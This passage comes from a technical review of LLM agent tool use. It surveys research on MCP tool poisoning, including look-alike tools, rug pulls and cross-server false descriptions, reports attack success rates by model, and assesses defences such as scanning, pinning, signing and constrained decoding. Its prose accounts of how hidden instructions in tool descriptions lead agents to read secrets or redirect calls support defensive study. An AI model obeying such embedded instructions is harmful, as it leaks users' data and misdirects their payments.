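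Jawad and Brunel also tried six defences against a version of the attack that added 100 tools, one of which GPT-4o chose in 84.8% of cases. A filter for prompt injection changed nothing, because the descriptions contained no instructions. Ranking tools partly by reputation lowered the rate to 68.8%. Allowing each publisher at most two places in the results lowered it to 41.4%, but the test assumed that the attacker had one account, and an attacker can open several in a catalogue where accounts are free.

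A small catalogue can also contain a look-alike tool. Anbiaee, Dadkhah and Ghorbani (2026), in *When Tool Names Are Not Identities*, gave five models a legitimate tool for fetching datasets and one from an attacker's server. They varied the name, description and schema of the attacker's tool and ran 50 trials per model for each of twelve combinations. When the attacker's tool copied the name and description and accepted the same arguments, GPT-5.4, Qwen3.7 Max and DeepSeek V3 used the attacker's server every time. Gemini 2.5 Pro did so in 84% of trials. Claude Sonnet 5 did so in 6% and asked the user for clarification in the rest. When the copy required unrelated arguments, no model chose it, so the schema also influences selection.

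Choosing at random between two identical entries would select the attacker's tool 50% of the time. The order of the list, or the way the host handled duplicate names, probably accounts for the rest of the 100% rates, so they do not show that models prefer the attacker's tool. In a more informative test, the attacker's tool had an unrelated name, a description that claimed official approval, and compatible arguments. DeepSeek V3 chose it in 50% of trials, Gemini in 42%, Qwen in 20% and GPT-5.4 in 4%. Claude never chose it, though it asked for clarification in 22% of trials. With five other unrelated names, GPT-5.4's average rose to 25%, so its low rate depended partly on the name. Prefixing tool names with their server, as MCP advises, would distinguish identical names but would not indicate which server the user trusts.

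### Three kinds of hostile description

A look-alike can harm the user only if the agent calls it, but in tool poisoning, a tool's description can also affect calls to other tools. Luca Beurer-Kellner and Marc Fischer of the security company Invariant Labs drew attention to this attack in April 2025. In the simplest case, the description of a seemingly useful tool also contains instructions to the model, such as to read a private file before starting the user's task. The user may see only the tool's name, while the model reads the whole description. If the host loads all descriptions at the start, the attack can work without any call to the poisoned tool. If the host searches a catalogue first, the search must return the poisoned description for the attack to work.

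In a "rug pull", the server changes a tool's description after the user has approved a harmless version. *ETDI* (2025), a proposal for securing tool definitions, attributes the problem to hosts that remember an approval by the tool's name or version and do not recheck the full definition. The term also covers a provider that changes what the tool does without changing its description.

In a cross-server attack, one server's description changes how the agent uses another server's tool. Suppose the shop's agent also has an exchange-rate tool from an outside server run by a customer, who has falsely written in the tool's description that the shop's refund tool takes amounts in cents. The shop's own description gives no unit, so it doesn't contradict the claim. The agent sends 2000 for a 20-euro refund, and because the tool actually takes euros, the customer collects 2,000 euros. The shop's server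 is not malicious, and the agent may never have called the exchange-rate tool.

Argument validation misses all three attacks because it checks the finished call, not why the model made it. The call `issue_refund("A-1043", 2000)` passes, just as it did when it was an honest mistake. A poisoned request to read a private file also passes if the path is a valid string. The attacker only has to get the model to make a different valid call. Tighter schemas help when they exclude the harmful value, as a list of permitted email recipients can, but not when another user might legitimately send the same value.

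### MCPTox

*MCPTox* (Wang, Gao and colleagues, 2025) was the first large measurement of tool poisoning. The team used language models to help write 1,348 test cases for 45 real MCP servers with 353 tools, then checked the cases by hand. (The paper's breakdown by type adds up to 1,497 cases, with no explanation for the difference.) Each case paired an ordinary user request with a poisoned tool, whose description the team added to the server's list of real tools. The harmful action always had to go through one of the real tools.

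The cases fall into three types. In the first, the user asks for something the poisoned tool supposedly does, and its description leads the model to call a different tool. In the second, the poisoned tool looks like a background process, and its description sets a rule for a common action, such as requiring the model to read a secret key before any file operation. In the third, the description leads the model to change a parameter of a call the user wanted, such as the recipient of an email.

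The team gave each case to 20 "agents", which were 16 models, four of them tested with reasoning switched on and off. It recorded the calls that the model wrote, without needing to execute them, and sorted the outcomes into four groups:

| Outcome | What the model did | Counted as |
|---|---|---|
| Success | Called a real tool to carry out the harmful action | Success |
| Ignored | Did what the user asked | Failure |
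| Direct execution | Called the poisoned tool itself | Failure |
| Refused | Identified the instruction as suspicious and declined | Failure |

The success rate is the number of successes divided by the number of valid outputs. Excluding invalid outputs keeps a model from appearing safe just because it writes broken calls. But the scoring counts direct execution as a failed attack, even though the agent has called an attacker's tool and may have sent it data. Direct execution made up 18.9% of the failures.

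The average success rate was 36.5%, and the highest was 72.8%, for OpenAI's o1-mini. Attacks that changed parameters succeeded most often, at 46.7%. Argument validation is least suited to catching this type, since the agent calls the tool that the user wanted and a redirected email still has a well-formed address. Models seldom refused, and even Claude 3.7 Sonnet, which had the highest refusal rate, refused less than 3% of the time. Most failed attacks therefore failed because the model overlooked the instruction or called the wrong tool.

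Wang, Gao and colleagues conclude that more capable models are often more susceptible because they follow instructions better. Within one model family, the evidence that reasoning increases susceptibility is strong. Turning reasoning on raised the attack success rate for all four sizes of Alibaba's Qwen3, for example from 23.7% to 58.5% for the 32-billion-parameter version. The evidence that larger models are more susceptible is weaker. Without reasoning, the rate did not rise steadily with size, and was 14.0%, 5.1%, 23.7% and 17.2% from the smallest Qwen3 to the largest. Between families, Phi-4, a fairly small model, reached 70.2%, while the stronger Claude 3.7 Sonnet reached 34.3%. Some weak models probably resisted only because they could not follow a conditional instruction buried in a long list of tools, and they would lose that protection once they improved.

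### Measurements on 2026 models

In *MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks*, Shaikh and Montaruli (2026) tested newer models in July 2026 and executed the tool calls they made. They combined 18 models with 45 attacks and 12 ways of building a host. Eleven of these used software libraries known as frameworks, and the twelfth used OpenAI's interface directly. Each run gave the agent a harmless task, an honest server with tools for files and web requests, a hostile server, and a folder containing a planted secret. A test server stood in for the attacker's server and logged everything it received.

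Of the 9,215 runs that produced a verdict, the attack succeeded in 2,113, or 22.9%. The models differed enormously:

| Model | Success rate of the attacks |
|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.4% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 1.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 1.9% |
| DeepSeek-R1 | 3.6% |
| GPT-5.5 | 12.4% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 14.5% |
| Mistral Large 2 | 21.6% |
| Mistral Large 3 | 43.7% |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 44.1% |
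| Amazon Nova Pro | 49.7% |

"Success" covers several degrees of harm. In 255 runs, under 3% of all runs, the planted secret reached the test server. In another 487, the test server received a request without the secret. In the remaining 1,371 successes, the host sent a call that did what the attacker wanted, but the test server received nothing. Most of these calls went to tools on the hostile server that only recorded them, so the set-up partly explains why so few secrets were stolen.

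The results do not support a general link between capability and susceptibility. Anthropic's newer models resisted far better than its older ones, whereas Mistral Large 3 failed twice as often as its predecessor. Shaikh and Montaruli consider training against such attacks the most plausible cause of the difference, but they did not test this. The attacks also came from published techniques, which newer models may have seen in training, so the low failure rates may not hold for unfamiliar attacks. Even a model that recognizes an attack may comply with it, as Claude Sonnet 5 did in four of its ten failures, when it called the instruction a prompt injection and then made the harmful call.

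The rates in the two studies are not directly comparable. DeepSeek-R1 scored 70.9% in MCPTox and 3.6% in the other study. Such a large gap between results under the same model name must come mainly from differences in the attacks, scoring and set-up, so the fall in the average from 36.5% to 22.9% is not evidence that agents have become safer. Comparisons within each study are more reliable.

The choice of framework mattered less than the choice of model. Nine of the twelve set-ups had overall rates between 23.4% and 26.1%, though individual models varied more. No framework checked descriptions for attacks. Pydantic AI had a rate of 16.6% because it does not allow two tools with the same name, which blocked 14 of the 45 attacks before any text reached the model. Its type checks did not help, because a description containing hostile instructions is still a valid string. AG2 had the lowest rate,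 4.6%, but only because it rarely completed the outgoing call that the model had requested.

### Scanning descriptions

The simplest defence is to check descriptions before the model reads them. Shaikh and Montaruli built a scanner that flags text that reads like an instruction to use another tool or web address, text in certain encodings, and descriptions longer than 500 characters. It rejected 20 of the 45 attacks and wrongly flagged 9 of 125 harmless descriptions. Six of those nine told the model to use a related tool, which is useful advice.

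The scanner missed attacks phrased as company policy, attacks written in another language, and attacks placed outside the description, such as in a tool's result. It would also miss the false claim about cents, which looks like ordinary documentation. The attacks were not written to evade this scanner, and an attacker who can run it beforehand can keep rewording a description until it passes. A language model could scan more flexibly, but it would have to judge whether a plausible statement about someone else's tool is true.

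### Pinning an approved definition

Pinning addresses changes after approval. When the user approves a tool, the host puts its definition into a standard form, so that irrelevant differences such as the order of fields don't matter, and computes a hash, a short fingerprint that changes if any part of the definition changes:

```
pin = SHA-256(name + description + inputSchema + annotations)
```

The host stores the pin with the server's identity. Whenever it fetches the tool list again, it recomputes the hash and blocks the tool if the hash differs from the pin. The hash has to cover the whole schema, because its fields have descriptions too. The host also has to treat a new tool as a change. The check needs no language model and takes almost no time.

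A matching hash shows only that the definition is the one the user approved. If the exchange-rate tool's description contained the false claim about cents from the start, the hash would still match. A mismatch is also weak evidence of an attack, since honest developers revise their tools. *MCPEvol-Bench* (2026) collected successive versions of 515 servers and sorted the changes into 18 patterns, including rewritten descriptions and added, replaced and removed tools. Public registries offer little help in distinguishing honest changes from malicious ones. According to *Same Name, Different Server* (2026), the MCP registry keeps versions of a server's description, packages and addresses but not of its tool definitions.

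### Signing definitions

A digital signature lets the host check who wrote a definition, which a hash does not. The publisher signs the definition with a private key, and the host verifies the signature with the matching public key. An impostor who copies the shop's refund tool cannot produce the shop's signature, so a host that knows the shop's key can reject the copy. The publisher can also sign an honest update, so the host can tell it from tampering by an outsider.

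*Verifiable Manifest Signing and Transparency Enforcement for Secure MCP-Based LLM Pipelines* (2026) extends this to individual calls. The system turns each tool request into a manifest, a structured record of what the user sees, what the model's side will execute and how recent the request is. It signs only manifests that comply with policy, and verifies them before execution. Outside auditors can later check whether a call was authorized and unaltered.

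A signature does not stop the publisher, or anyone who has stolen the publisher's key, from signing a malicious tool. *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (2026) points out that when users install a tool as a signed package, the signature covers a hidden routine or a compromised library along with the rest of the code. A signature guarantees less for a remote tool, because the user receives the signed definition but not the program.

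### Asking again after a change

When a pin or signature no longer matches, the host can suspend the tool and ask the user to approve it again. *ETDI* lists the lack of such a prompt among the weaknesses behind rug pulls. A useful prompt would show the old and new text side by side, not just the tool's name, so the user could notice that an exchange-rate tool has started to give advice about refunds.

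What the user sees may also differ from what the model receives, because some characters are invisible on screen but still reach the model. *Unicode TAG-Block Concealment of Tool-Metadata Payloads in the Model Context Protocol* (2026) calls this an "approval-view fidelity gap". The host can close it by removing such characters or displaying them as codes. In Shaikh and Montaruli's tests, "Unicode encoding" attacks failed in all 209 runs, so plain sentences that nobody reads closely may be the greater danger. If every legitimate update triggers a prompt, users will have more to read and more reason to approve without reading.

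Frameworks could build in these checks, but their developers have mostly placed the responsibility elsewhere. Shaikh and Montaruli sent five reports to four organizations, which rejected all of them. The maintainers of the MCP SDK replied that the host's review of tool calls protects against rug pulls. LangChain replied that its library should pass on information unchanged from the server. Microsoft and deepset, which develops the Haystack framework, treat the servers that a user connects as trusted, an assumption that suits a company's own servers better than those run by strangers.

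### Changes that leave the description alone

All of these defences examine the tool's definition, but a remote server can change its behaviour without changing the definition. *ProbeID* (2026) repeated the same test calls to tools on 16 servers over several weeks. From day 22 onward, seven tools consistently gave different responses than they had at the start. Every server still reported the same version number, so a host that had pinned the version would not have detected any of the differences. Some of them may be harmless, since a tool that reports live data should not always return the same answer.

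Ordinary software releases can have the same effect. *When Valid Tool Calls Change Meaning* (2026) compared two versions of GitHub's MCP server. Both create a repository when the request gives only a name, but version 1.4 makes it private and version 1.3 makes it public. Suppose a host reads the definition from version 1.4, the user approves it, and the model leaves out the privacy setting because private is the default. If the operator rolls the server back to version 1.3 before the call arrives, the server accepts the call and makes the repository public. Fetching the definition again would have revealed this change, but the study also found releases with identical relevant definitions and different effects.

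## Getting the arguments right

An agent can pick the right tool from an honest server and still fill in the arguments wrongly. The table shows how this can happen with the refund tool. For the row on enumerations (fixed lists of permitted values), suppose the shop has added a `reason` field that accepts only `damaged`, `late` or `other`.

| Fault | Example | Result of an automatic check |
|---|---|---|
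| Tool that does not exist | `refund_order("A-1043", 20)` | Rejected |
| Missing field | No `amount` | Rejected |
| Invented field | An extra `currency: "cents"` | Accepted unless the schema forbids extra fields |
| Wrong type | `amount: "20 euros"` | Rejected |
| Value outside an enumeration | `reason: "broken lamp"` | Rejected |
| Well-typed value with the wrong meaning | `amount: 2000` for 20 euros | Accepted |
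| Outdated schema | `amount`, after the shop has renamed the field `amount_eur` | Accepted by the host, probably rejected by the server |

Researchers classify argument errors in different ways. *Diagnosing with Insights* (2026) puts most of them in one class, the "invocation issue". A run has this fault if at least one of its calls fails a test called `schemaOK`, which checks for compliance with the schema, incompatible combinations of fields, and errors that the tool reports. A wrong value that complies with the schema is therefore left out unless the tool reports an error. *ToolCritic* (2025) separates errors in required arguments from errors in optional ones, because errors in required arguments usually come from misreading the user's request or the tool's specification, while errors in optional arguments may concern only minor settings.

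In *Measuring What Tool-Using LLM Agents Actually Do*, Gurram (2026) tested how much harm one wrong argument does. Gurram ran each task twice with the same model. In the second run, a program replaced one argument of the first call with a wrong value that still fitted the schema, such as Manchester for London or another patient's identifier. The agent then saw the result and could correct the mistake. Across 1,085 pairs of runs and seven models, the error rate rose from 52.4% to 74.5%. Where the altered call ran without any error message, the error rate rose by 44.7 percentage points.

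The error rate in the normal runs is high partly because the prompts left out the parameter schemas. The agents had to guess field names and wrote `duration` where the tool expected `duration_minutes`. The comparison between the paired runs is more reliable than either rate alone. Gurram also had three language models grade the same answers, and they found a rise of only 2.5 points. The graders compared each answer with a description of the task instead of the correct values, so they could accept a plausible temperature for the wrong city.

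Outdated schemas are a practical concern because tools change often. In the server histories that *MCPEvol-Bench* collected, developers had modified 32.5% of the original tools by the latest version and withdrawn another 22.1%. When the benchmark simulated such updates and gave agents the same tasks before and after, GPT-5.4's score fell by 13.7% and Claude Sonnet 4.6's by 14.4%. Those agents could read the new definitions, so the drops measure the difficulty of working with a changed set of tools, not the effect of outdated schemas.

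### Validating a finished call

A schema validator is an ordinary program that compares a call with the schema, rule by rule. Suppose the shop publishes a stricter schema than before:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "order_id": { "type": "string", "pattern": "^A-[0-9]+$" },
    "amount":   { "type": "integer", "minimum": 1 },
    "reason":   { "enum": ["damaged", "late", "other"] }
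  },
  "required": ["order_id", "amount"],
  "additionalProperties": false
}
```

The validator first checks that the arguments form an object and that both required fields are present. It then checks each value against the rules for its field. The `pattern` rule requires an order number to be "A-" followed by digits. The last line forbids fields that the schema does not list. Without that line, JSON Schema permits them, so an agent could add `currency: "cents"`, pass validation, and proceed as if the server had used that field when it had not.

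If the agent sends `amount: "20 euros"`, the validator reports a string where an integer is required, and the model can try again. If the agent sends `amount: 2000`, every check succeeds because both required fields are present, the order number matches the pattern, and 2000 is an integer of at least 1.

An upper limit of 500 would stop this call, but it would also stop a legitimate refund for a 2,000-euro sofa and let through a 3-euro refund that the agent had sent as 300. The right limit depends on the order, so a schema that is the same for every order cannot specify it.

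### Constraining the text as the model writes it

Validation finds an error after the model has made it. Constrained decoding prevents the error while the model is writing. A language model writes one token at a time, where a token is a word, part of a word, or a symbol. At each step it assigns a probability to every token in its vocabulary, and the software picks the next token from that distribution. A constrained decoder first works out which tokens could continue the text without breaking the schema. It sets the probability of all others to zero and scales up the rest so that they again add up to 1:

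```
p'(t) = m(t) · p(t) / Σ m(u) · p(u)
```

Here p(t) is the model's original probability for token t, m(t) is 1 if the token is allowed and 0 otherwise, and the sum runs over all tokens u. In practice, as *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) explains, the software sets the scores of forbidden tokens to minus infinity before converting scores into probabilities, which has the same effect. It can also compute the lists of allowed tokens once per schema and look them up at each step, so the check need not slow the model much.

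Suppose the model has written `"order_id": "A-1043", "amount":` and must now choose the next token. The probabilities below are invented, and the example treats each number as one token.

| Next token | Original probability | Allowed? | New probability |
|---|---|---|---|
| `2000` | 0.45 | Yes | 0.45 / 0.70 = 0.64 |
| `20` | 0.25 | Yes | 0.25 / 0.70 = 0.36 |
| `"` (the start of a text such as "20 euros") | 0.25 | No | 0 |
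| `twenty` | 0.05 | No | 0 |

The two allowed tokens had a combined probability of 0.70, so the decoder divides each token's probability by 0.70. The call is now certain to contain an integer, but the chance that the integer is 2000 has risen from 45% to 64%. The finished call passes validation because the decoder and the validator apply the same rules.

In this example, the constraint has also removed a useful error. Without the constraint, the model would have started to write "20 euros" a quarter of the time. The validator would have rejected that with a message that the value must be an integer, and the model would probably have then sent just 20, the correct amount. With the constraint, the model never writes the unit, so neither the server nor anyone reading the log can detect that the amount was meant in euros.

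*STAGE* (2026) and other recent work support the distinction between form and content. When *STAGE* applied a grammar to a small Qwen model that turned documents into JSON, more of the output fitted the schema, but the values did not become more accurate. Training the model for the task improved the fit and raised the accuracy of the values by 22 points. Adding the grammar to the trained model lowered that accuracy by two points.

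Constrained decoding does not guarantee even correctly formed arguments, because the decoder looks only one token ahead and can allow a token that doesn't lead to a complete output. *Correctness-Guaranteed Code Generation via Constrained Decoding* (2025) gives the example of a model that writes spaces forever, since JSON permits another space at many points. In the tests of *Stay Within Your Bounds* (2026), models kept opening new nested objects and lists without closing them. Raising the limit on output length from 512 to 4,096 tokens barely helped, and the share of outputs that satisfied the schema stayed well below 100% for every existing method.

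Masking also changes which valid answer the model gives. If a host generated whole calls and discarded the invalid ones, the valid calls would keep the relative probabilities the model gave them. A decoder that masks token by token can instead commit the model to an opening whose only valid endings are unlikely. *The Format Tax* (2026) notes that computing the undistorted distribution exactly is intractable, though several methods approximate it.

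A decoder that enforces a JSON schema can also prevent tool calls. Some models mark the start of a tool call with a tag, and *Constraint Tax in Open-Weight LLMs* (2026) points out that the decoder blocks this tag if the host requires the whole reply to fit the schema. The model then cannot call the tool and can only write an answer that looks complete.

The party that runs the model has to apply the constraint, because doing so requires the model's probabilities at every step. *Grammar-Constrained Decoding for Structured NLP Tasks without Finetuning* (2023) could not use the method with OpenAI's models for this reason. Providers have since built constrained decoding into their services, but a host's developer then depends on the provider to support every keyword in the schema. *JSONSchemaBench* (2025) therefore compares the declared schema support of six decoding frameworks with how well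 their output complies.

### Prose, schemas and structured errors

A schema can also help by telling the model more clearly what to write. This effect is hard to measure because a tool with a schema usually comes with more information than a tool without one. In *Schema First Tool APIs for LLM Agents* (March 2026), Sigdel and Baral tried to isolate it. They wrote one master specification for each tool and generated the other formats from it, so that every version contained the same facts. They also kept the tools themselves the same.

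The agent had to diagnose faults in a simulated software system by searching logs, reading files and running tests. It had a budget of 3, 5, 8 or 12 steps. The first group of runs described the tools in prose, and the second used JSON Schema. The third used the same schemas but answered a malformed call with a structured error that named the faulty field.

To judge whether a valid call was also sensible, Sigdel and Baral listed acceptable sequences of calls for each task. They counted a valid call as wrong if it fitted none of these sequences. The table gives the average number of calls per run, over all budgets.

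| | Prose | Schema | Schema with structured errors |
|---|---|---|---|
| Malformed calls | 5.39 | 3.72 | 3.72 |
| Valid calls that failed when executed | 0.54 | 0.00 | 0.00 |
| Valid but wrong calls | 0.93 | 3.03 | 3.03 |
| Tasks solved | 0% | 0% | 0% |

Schemas cut malformed calls by almost a third, but wrong calls more than tripled. If no call counts twice, the three kinds of failure add up to 6.9 per run with prose and 6.8 with schemas, while the average budget was seven steps. Schemas therefore seem to have turned malformed calls into valid but useless ones without reducing the total. They did not necessarily make the model's judgment worse. Only a valid call can be checked for whether it was sensible, so an agent that writes more valid calls has more chances to make a wrong one.

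Structured errors made no difference to any of the averages. However, the study was a pilot with a single model, a compressed version of Qwen2.5 with half a billion parameters, which is tiny by current standards. The model solved none of the eight tasks in any run, so the study cannot show whether schemas or better errors help an agent finish its work. Error messages that had no effect on this model might help a larger one. The software always picked the most likely token, so the runs with three different random seeds may have been nearly identical and added little evidence. Sigdel and Baral limit their claims to this model and set-up.

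### Retrieval and constraints for web requests

*Mitigating Errors in LLM-Generated Web API Invocations* (Maninger, Chemnitz and colleagues, July 2026), a larger study, tested constrained decoding on web APIs described in OpenAPI. It used 24 open models and 395 tasks, one for each operation of Asana, Google Calendar, Google Sheets and Slack. The models wrote each request as a line of JavaScript, which is harder than a typical tool call because the arguments can go in the web address, the headers or the body of the request.

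The team compared two kinds of help, retrieval and constrained decoding. Retrieval added the documentation of the five best-matching operations to the prompt, and the right one was among them 95% of the time. For constrained decoding, the team's software translated the OpenAPI document into patterns that the output had to match. If the model chose a method such as POST, it could then write only addresses that accept POST. After writing an address, it could use only that operation's fields and had to include all the required ones before closing the list.

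In half of the tests, the model had to choose both the operation and its arguments. In the other half, the prompt already contained the right operation. A request counted as correct only if it matched the reference solution exactly.

| | Requests correct, model chose the operation | Requests correct, operation given |
|---|---|---|
| No help | 13% | 26% |
| Retrieval | 22% | about 26% |
| Constrained decoding | 28% | 57% |

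Without constrained decoding, 31% of the operations that models chose did not exist, and when the operation was given, 39% of requests contained an invented field. Constrained decoding reduced both figures to zero, as its design guarantees. It also made some models competitive with stronger ones. When the operation was given, Code Llama 70B with constraints got 72% of requests completely right, compared with 59% for GPT-4o without them. The averages in the first column are only roughly comparable because they exclude models that produced no runnable code, and several models excluded without constraints are included with them.

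Retrieval also reduced invented fields, but it led models to fill in fields that the task did not need. For example, the documentation of every Asana operation includes `opt_pretty`, an optional setting that makes replies easier for a person to read, and models that had just read it several times tended to use it. Combining retrieval with constraints gave the best single results, 67% and 73%. But on average, the combination beat constraints alone only when the model also had to choose the operation.

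These results also give a rough estimate of how many errors constraints cannot prevent. With constraints, 81% of the requests in the first set-up ran, but only 28% were correct. So about half of all tasks ended in a valid request that ran without an error but did not match the solution. That share fell to about 28% when the operation was given. Some of these requests may have differed from the solution only by a harmless extra field, but requests with a wrong recipient or date would also be counted here.

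Constraints also had drawbacks. The share of requests that ran fell from 92% to 81% in the first set-up and from 98% to 85% in the second. On a second set of 28 tasks from real GitHub projects, constraints improved the average but made 6 of 23 models worse at the full task. Generation slowed from about 30 tokens a second to 7–10, although Maninger and colleagues used a simple prototype and expect better software to remove most of the delay. The models in the study are now old, and current ones probably invent far fewer fields.

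### Interfaces with realistic complications

Most tests of tool use give the agent tidy tools that always return clean results. *Beyond Perfect APIs* (2026) presents WildAGTEval, a benchmark that adds complications like those in commercial services. It has 86 functions for tasks such as controlling household devices, sending messages and shopping, and 300 conversations that together require 3,525 function calls. Four kinds of complication affect what the agent reads about a function, and four affect what the function returns.

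The researchers first tested one complication at a time. They gave the agent a correct history of the conversation and checked whether its next call was right. The table gives the average for ten models.

| Complication | Accuracy without it | Accuracy with it |
|---|---|---|
| Special formats, such as "UPS-16" for a parcel when the user says "16" | 66.3% | 58.5% |
| Functions with similar names but different purposes | 48.0% | 43.4% |
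| Notices and tips added to results | 75.3% | 73.4% |
| Irrelevant content, such as sponsored items, among results | 59.8% | 47.0% |

The paper reports the last drop as 27.3%, but it seems to have divided the loss by the lower score. Relative to the starting score, the drop is about 21%. Irrelevant content is still the most harmful of the four. In one example, a user asked for details of the fifth and seventh recipes in a list, and the agent fetched two sponsored recipes it had left out of that list. Both identifiers were valid, so the calls would have passed any schema check.

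The refund tool's fault is one of the eight complications. WildAGTEval calls it an "ambiguous description" and gives the example of a temperature field that omits the unit. The benchmark expects the agent to infer a "sensible default", which is reasonable for a thermostat because the user will notice a mistake and can reverse it. With a refund, it is better for the agent to ask. The researchers did not measure this complication separately, so the results do not show how often models guess the right unit.

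Some of the worst failures came after an error. When one agent could not look up a user's devices, it tried to play a film on device 4, then 3, then 2. Another could not retrieve the user's messages to find out who had written last, so it texted the first person in the contact list and reported success. The schema did not prevent either action, because a guessed device number and the first contact's number are both valid values. The strongest models in the study date from 2025, and newer ones may be more likely to stop after an error.

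### Learning a tool from recorded calls

Some tools have no usable documentation. An agent may be able to learn such a tool from a record of others' calls to it. Patel, Jagmohan and Vempaty (2025), in *Learning API Functionality from Demonstrations for Tool-based Agents*, tested this on three existing benchmarks covering office work, customer service for an online shop, and customer records. They replaced the documentation with demonstrations from successful runs by agents with access to the documentation. Each demonstration showed a call, the task it served and the steps before it.

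The team gave the agent the demonstrations themselves, documentation that a model had written from them, or that documentation together with the example calls. The table shows the share of tasks that OpenAI's o3-mini completed with five demonstrations per function.

| Material | Office work | Online shop | Customer records |
|---|---|---|---|
| Original documentation | 24% | 79% | 72% |
| Demonstrations | 42% | 48% | 69% |
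| Documentation written from demonstrations | 29% | 10% | 52% |
| The same, with example calls | 33% | 41% | 60% |

In the office tasks, demonstrations appear to work better than the original documentation. Patel and colleagues attribute this to the test tasks being so similar to the demonstrated ones that the agent could copy much of the answer. The shop tasks better show what happens when details matter. Adding more demonstrations often made results worse. In some tests they exceeded the amount of text the model could read, and in others an optional field appeared so often that the model writing the documentation described it as required.

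Most failures involved arguments. In the online shop, every order number had to begin with `#`. An agent that left it out received the message "Order not found", which didn't mention the missing `#`. A second model wrote guidelines based on the agent's practice, and in two trials these included advice to remove the `#`. The team then added the correct rule by hand, and the success rate rose from 10% to 49%. A one-line `pattern` in a schema would have stated the same rule, and a better error message might have let the agent find it without help.

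### Learning a tool by trying it

An agent with no record of earlier calls can experiment to learn how its tools work. *OpaqueToolsBench* (Hallinan, Venkatesh and colleagues, 2026) tests how much an agent can learn this way in three environments. The first uses simple functions, such as one that computes the area of a polygon, with meaningless names and no descriptions. In the second, the agent plays chess by choosing among several chess programs without knowing which is strong or which specializes in endgames. In the third, it looks for obscure facts using search engines that cover different subjects.

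Hallinan and colleagues also built a method called ToolObserver, in which the agent first attempts the task with whatever documentation it has. A second model, the editor, then reads the calls and results and rewrites the documentation, and the agent tries again. For the simple functions, the editor received only the tools' replies, not the correct answer. For chess and search, the agent could attempt training tasks first, and the editor also received feedback on how well each attempt had gone.

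ToolObserver worked well for the simple functions. With only meaningless names to start from, GPT-5 completed 80% of the tasks, compared with 44% for an earlier method that tested each tool separately. When GPT-5 had the descriptions but not the parameters, it completed none of the tasks at first, because it kept calling the functions without arguments. ToolObserver used error messages and results to work out which fields each function needed, which raised the completion rate to 86%, close to the 95% that GPT-5 reached with full documentation.

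The agent learned much less about behaviour that the fields did not reveal. With the specialized chess programs, ToolObserver raised the share of moves for which GPT-5 chose the best program from 23.5% to 40.1%, while full documentation gave 64.4%. When the programs differed only in strength, the share rose from 24.9% to 29.1%, against 100% with documentation. In the search tasks with every search engine available, accuracy barely changed, from 21.8% to 22.1%. The missing unit of the refund resembles these cases more than it resembles a missing field, because a call with the wrong unit looks just like a successful one.

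In all three environments, a bad call led only to an error message, a weak chess move or a wasted search. With many real tools, a call made to learn how the tool works also has real effects. Suppose the shop's agent calls `issue_refund("A-1043", 1)` to find out whether the amount is in euros or cents. The server replies "Refunded 1 on order A-1043". The customer has now received either one euro or one cent, and the agent can't tell which unless it can look at the account. GPT-5 needed an average of 3.4 rounds to finish learning the functions with meaningless names, and each round of practice with the refund tool could make another payment.

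A guessed argument is most dangerous when it happens to be valid. In one of Patel and colleagues' tests, a user asked the agent to delete a customer called Kerry Moore. The agent passed the name as the `customer_id` instead of looking up the number, and such a call can only fail because a name matches no customer number. If the agent had guessed a number, the call might have deleted someone else's record, and the reply would have confirmed the deletion without revealing the mistake. An agent should therefore learn from read-only calls where it can, or practise on test data.

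A simulator can also stand in for the real tool. In *Gecko* (2026), an ordinary program checks the arguments' types, and then a language model checks whether the arguments make sense. The model would catch an hour of 27, for example, but would probably accept the refund of 2000. It receives the call and the schema but not the user's request, and it is instructed to accept a value when in doubt.

### Identifiers that the model carries between calls

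An agent often has to refer back to something that an earlier call created. Now that MCP has no sessions, the server gives the model a state handle, an identifier that the model passes back in later calls. In Model Context Protocol's shopping basket example, the agent calls `create_basket`, the server returns a `basket_id`, and the model passes that identifier as an ordinary argument to `add_item`.

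Previously, a server could store the basket with the session, and the model never had to work with the identifier. The project considers the new arrangement more powerful in many cases, because the model can use an identifier with several tools or pass it to a later step. But the model can also get the identifier wrong. In a schema, a basket identifier is usually a string, like an order number or a customer's name, so a type check won't catch the error if the model puts an order number in its place.

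The shop can catch this kind of mix-up by giving each type of identifier its own form. If every basket identifier begins with `basket_` and the schema requires that pattern, the validator will reject an order number used in place of a basket identifier. However, the pattern cannot distinguish one basket from another. The model might copy the wrong identifier from a long conversation or guess one, as the WildAGTEval agent did with device numbers. An attacker could also plant another customer's identifier in text the agent reads.

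The server therefore has to check who owns the basket each time it receives the identifier:

```
add_item(basket_id, item):
    caller = user named in the verified login token
    basket = look up basket_id
    if basket does not exist or basket.owner ≠ caller:
        reject the call
    add item to basket
```

The caller's identity has to come from the login that accompanies the request, not from the arguments, because the model writes those and can be wrong or manipulated. Long random identifiers help because nobody can guess them, but they do not replace checking the caller's identity. Anyone who sees an identifier in a conversation, a log or an email can copy it.

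Ownership checks work best when the agent acts for a single customer. But the refund agent may use a staff account that can open every order in the shop. If it confuses order A-1043 with A-1034, the check passes because the account has access to both, and the server pays the wrong customer. To prevent this, the host could tie the conversation to one customer at the start and have the server reject refunds on anyone else's orders. The agent could still refund the wrong order if that customer has several.

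## Type-checking the code an agent writes before it runs

An agent that makes one call at a time has to copy each identifier from one result into the next call, and it may copy the wrong one. If the agent writes a short program instead, a variable carries the identifier:

```python
order = await find_order(customer="C-77", item="lamp")
await issue_refund(order_id=order["id"], amount=20)
```

The model never writes the order number, so it cannot miscopy A-1043 as A-1034. It can still look up the wrong customer, and it still has to choose the amount.

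Developers mostly let agents write programs for other reasons, such as speed. With ordinary tool calls, the model must read each result before writing the next call. Pydantic, which develops the Pydantic AI framework, tried both methods on a request to compare the weather in London and Paris, which required three tools in sequence. Claude Sonnet 4.5 took four rounds and 12.2 seconds with ordinary calls, compared with two rounds and 9.1 seconds when it wrote a program, and it read about a fifth fewer tokens with the program. This is one example from a company that develops an interpreter for such programs, but the saving should grow with the number of dependent steps.

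A program can also filter out data the model doesn't need to read. In an example from Pydantic's *Code Mode*, a program fetches ten items and returns only the three matching names. Varda and Pai, in a Cloudflare post also titled *Code Mode*, report that agents could handle more tools, and more complex ones, when they called the tools from code. They suggest that models' training data contains a great deal of real code but few realistic tool calls.

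### From a call to a program

A schema validator needs finished arguments, and many of a program's arguments do not exist until it runs. Suppose the shop asks the agent to refund everyone whose lamp arrived broken:

```python
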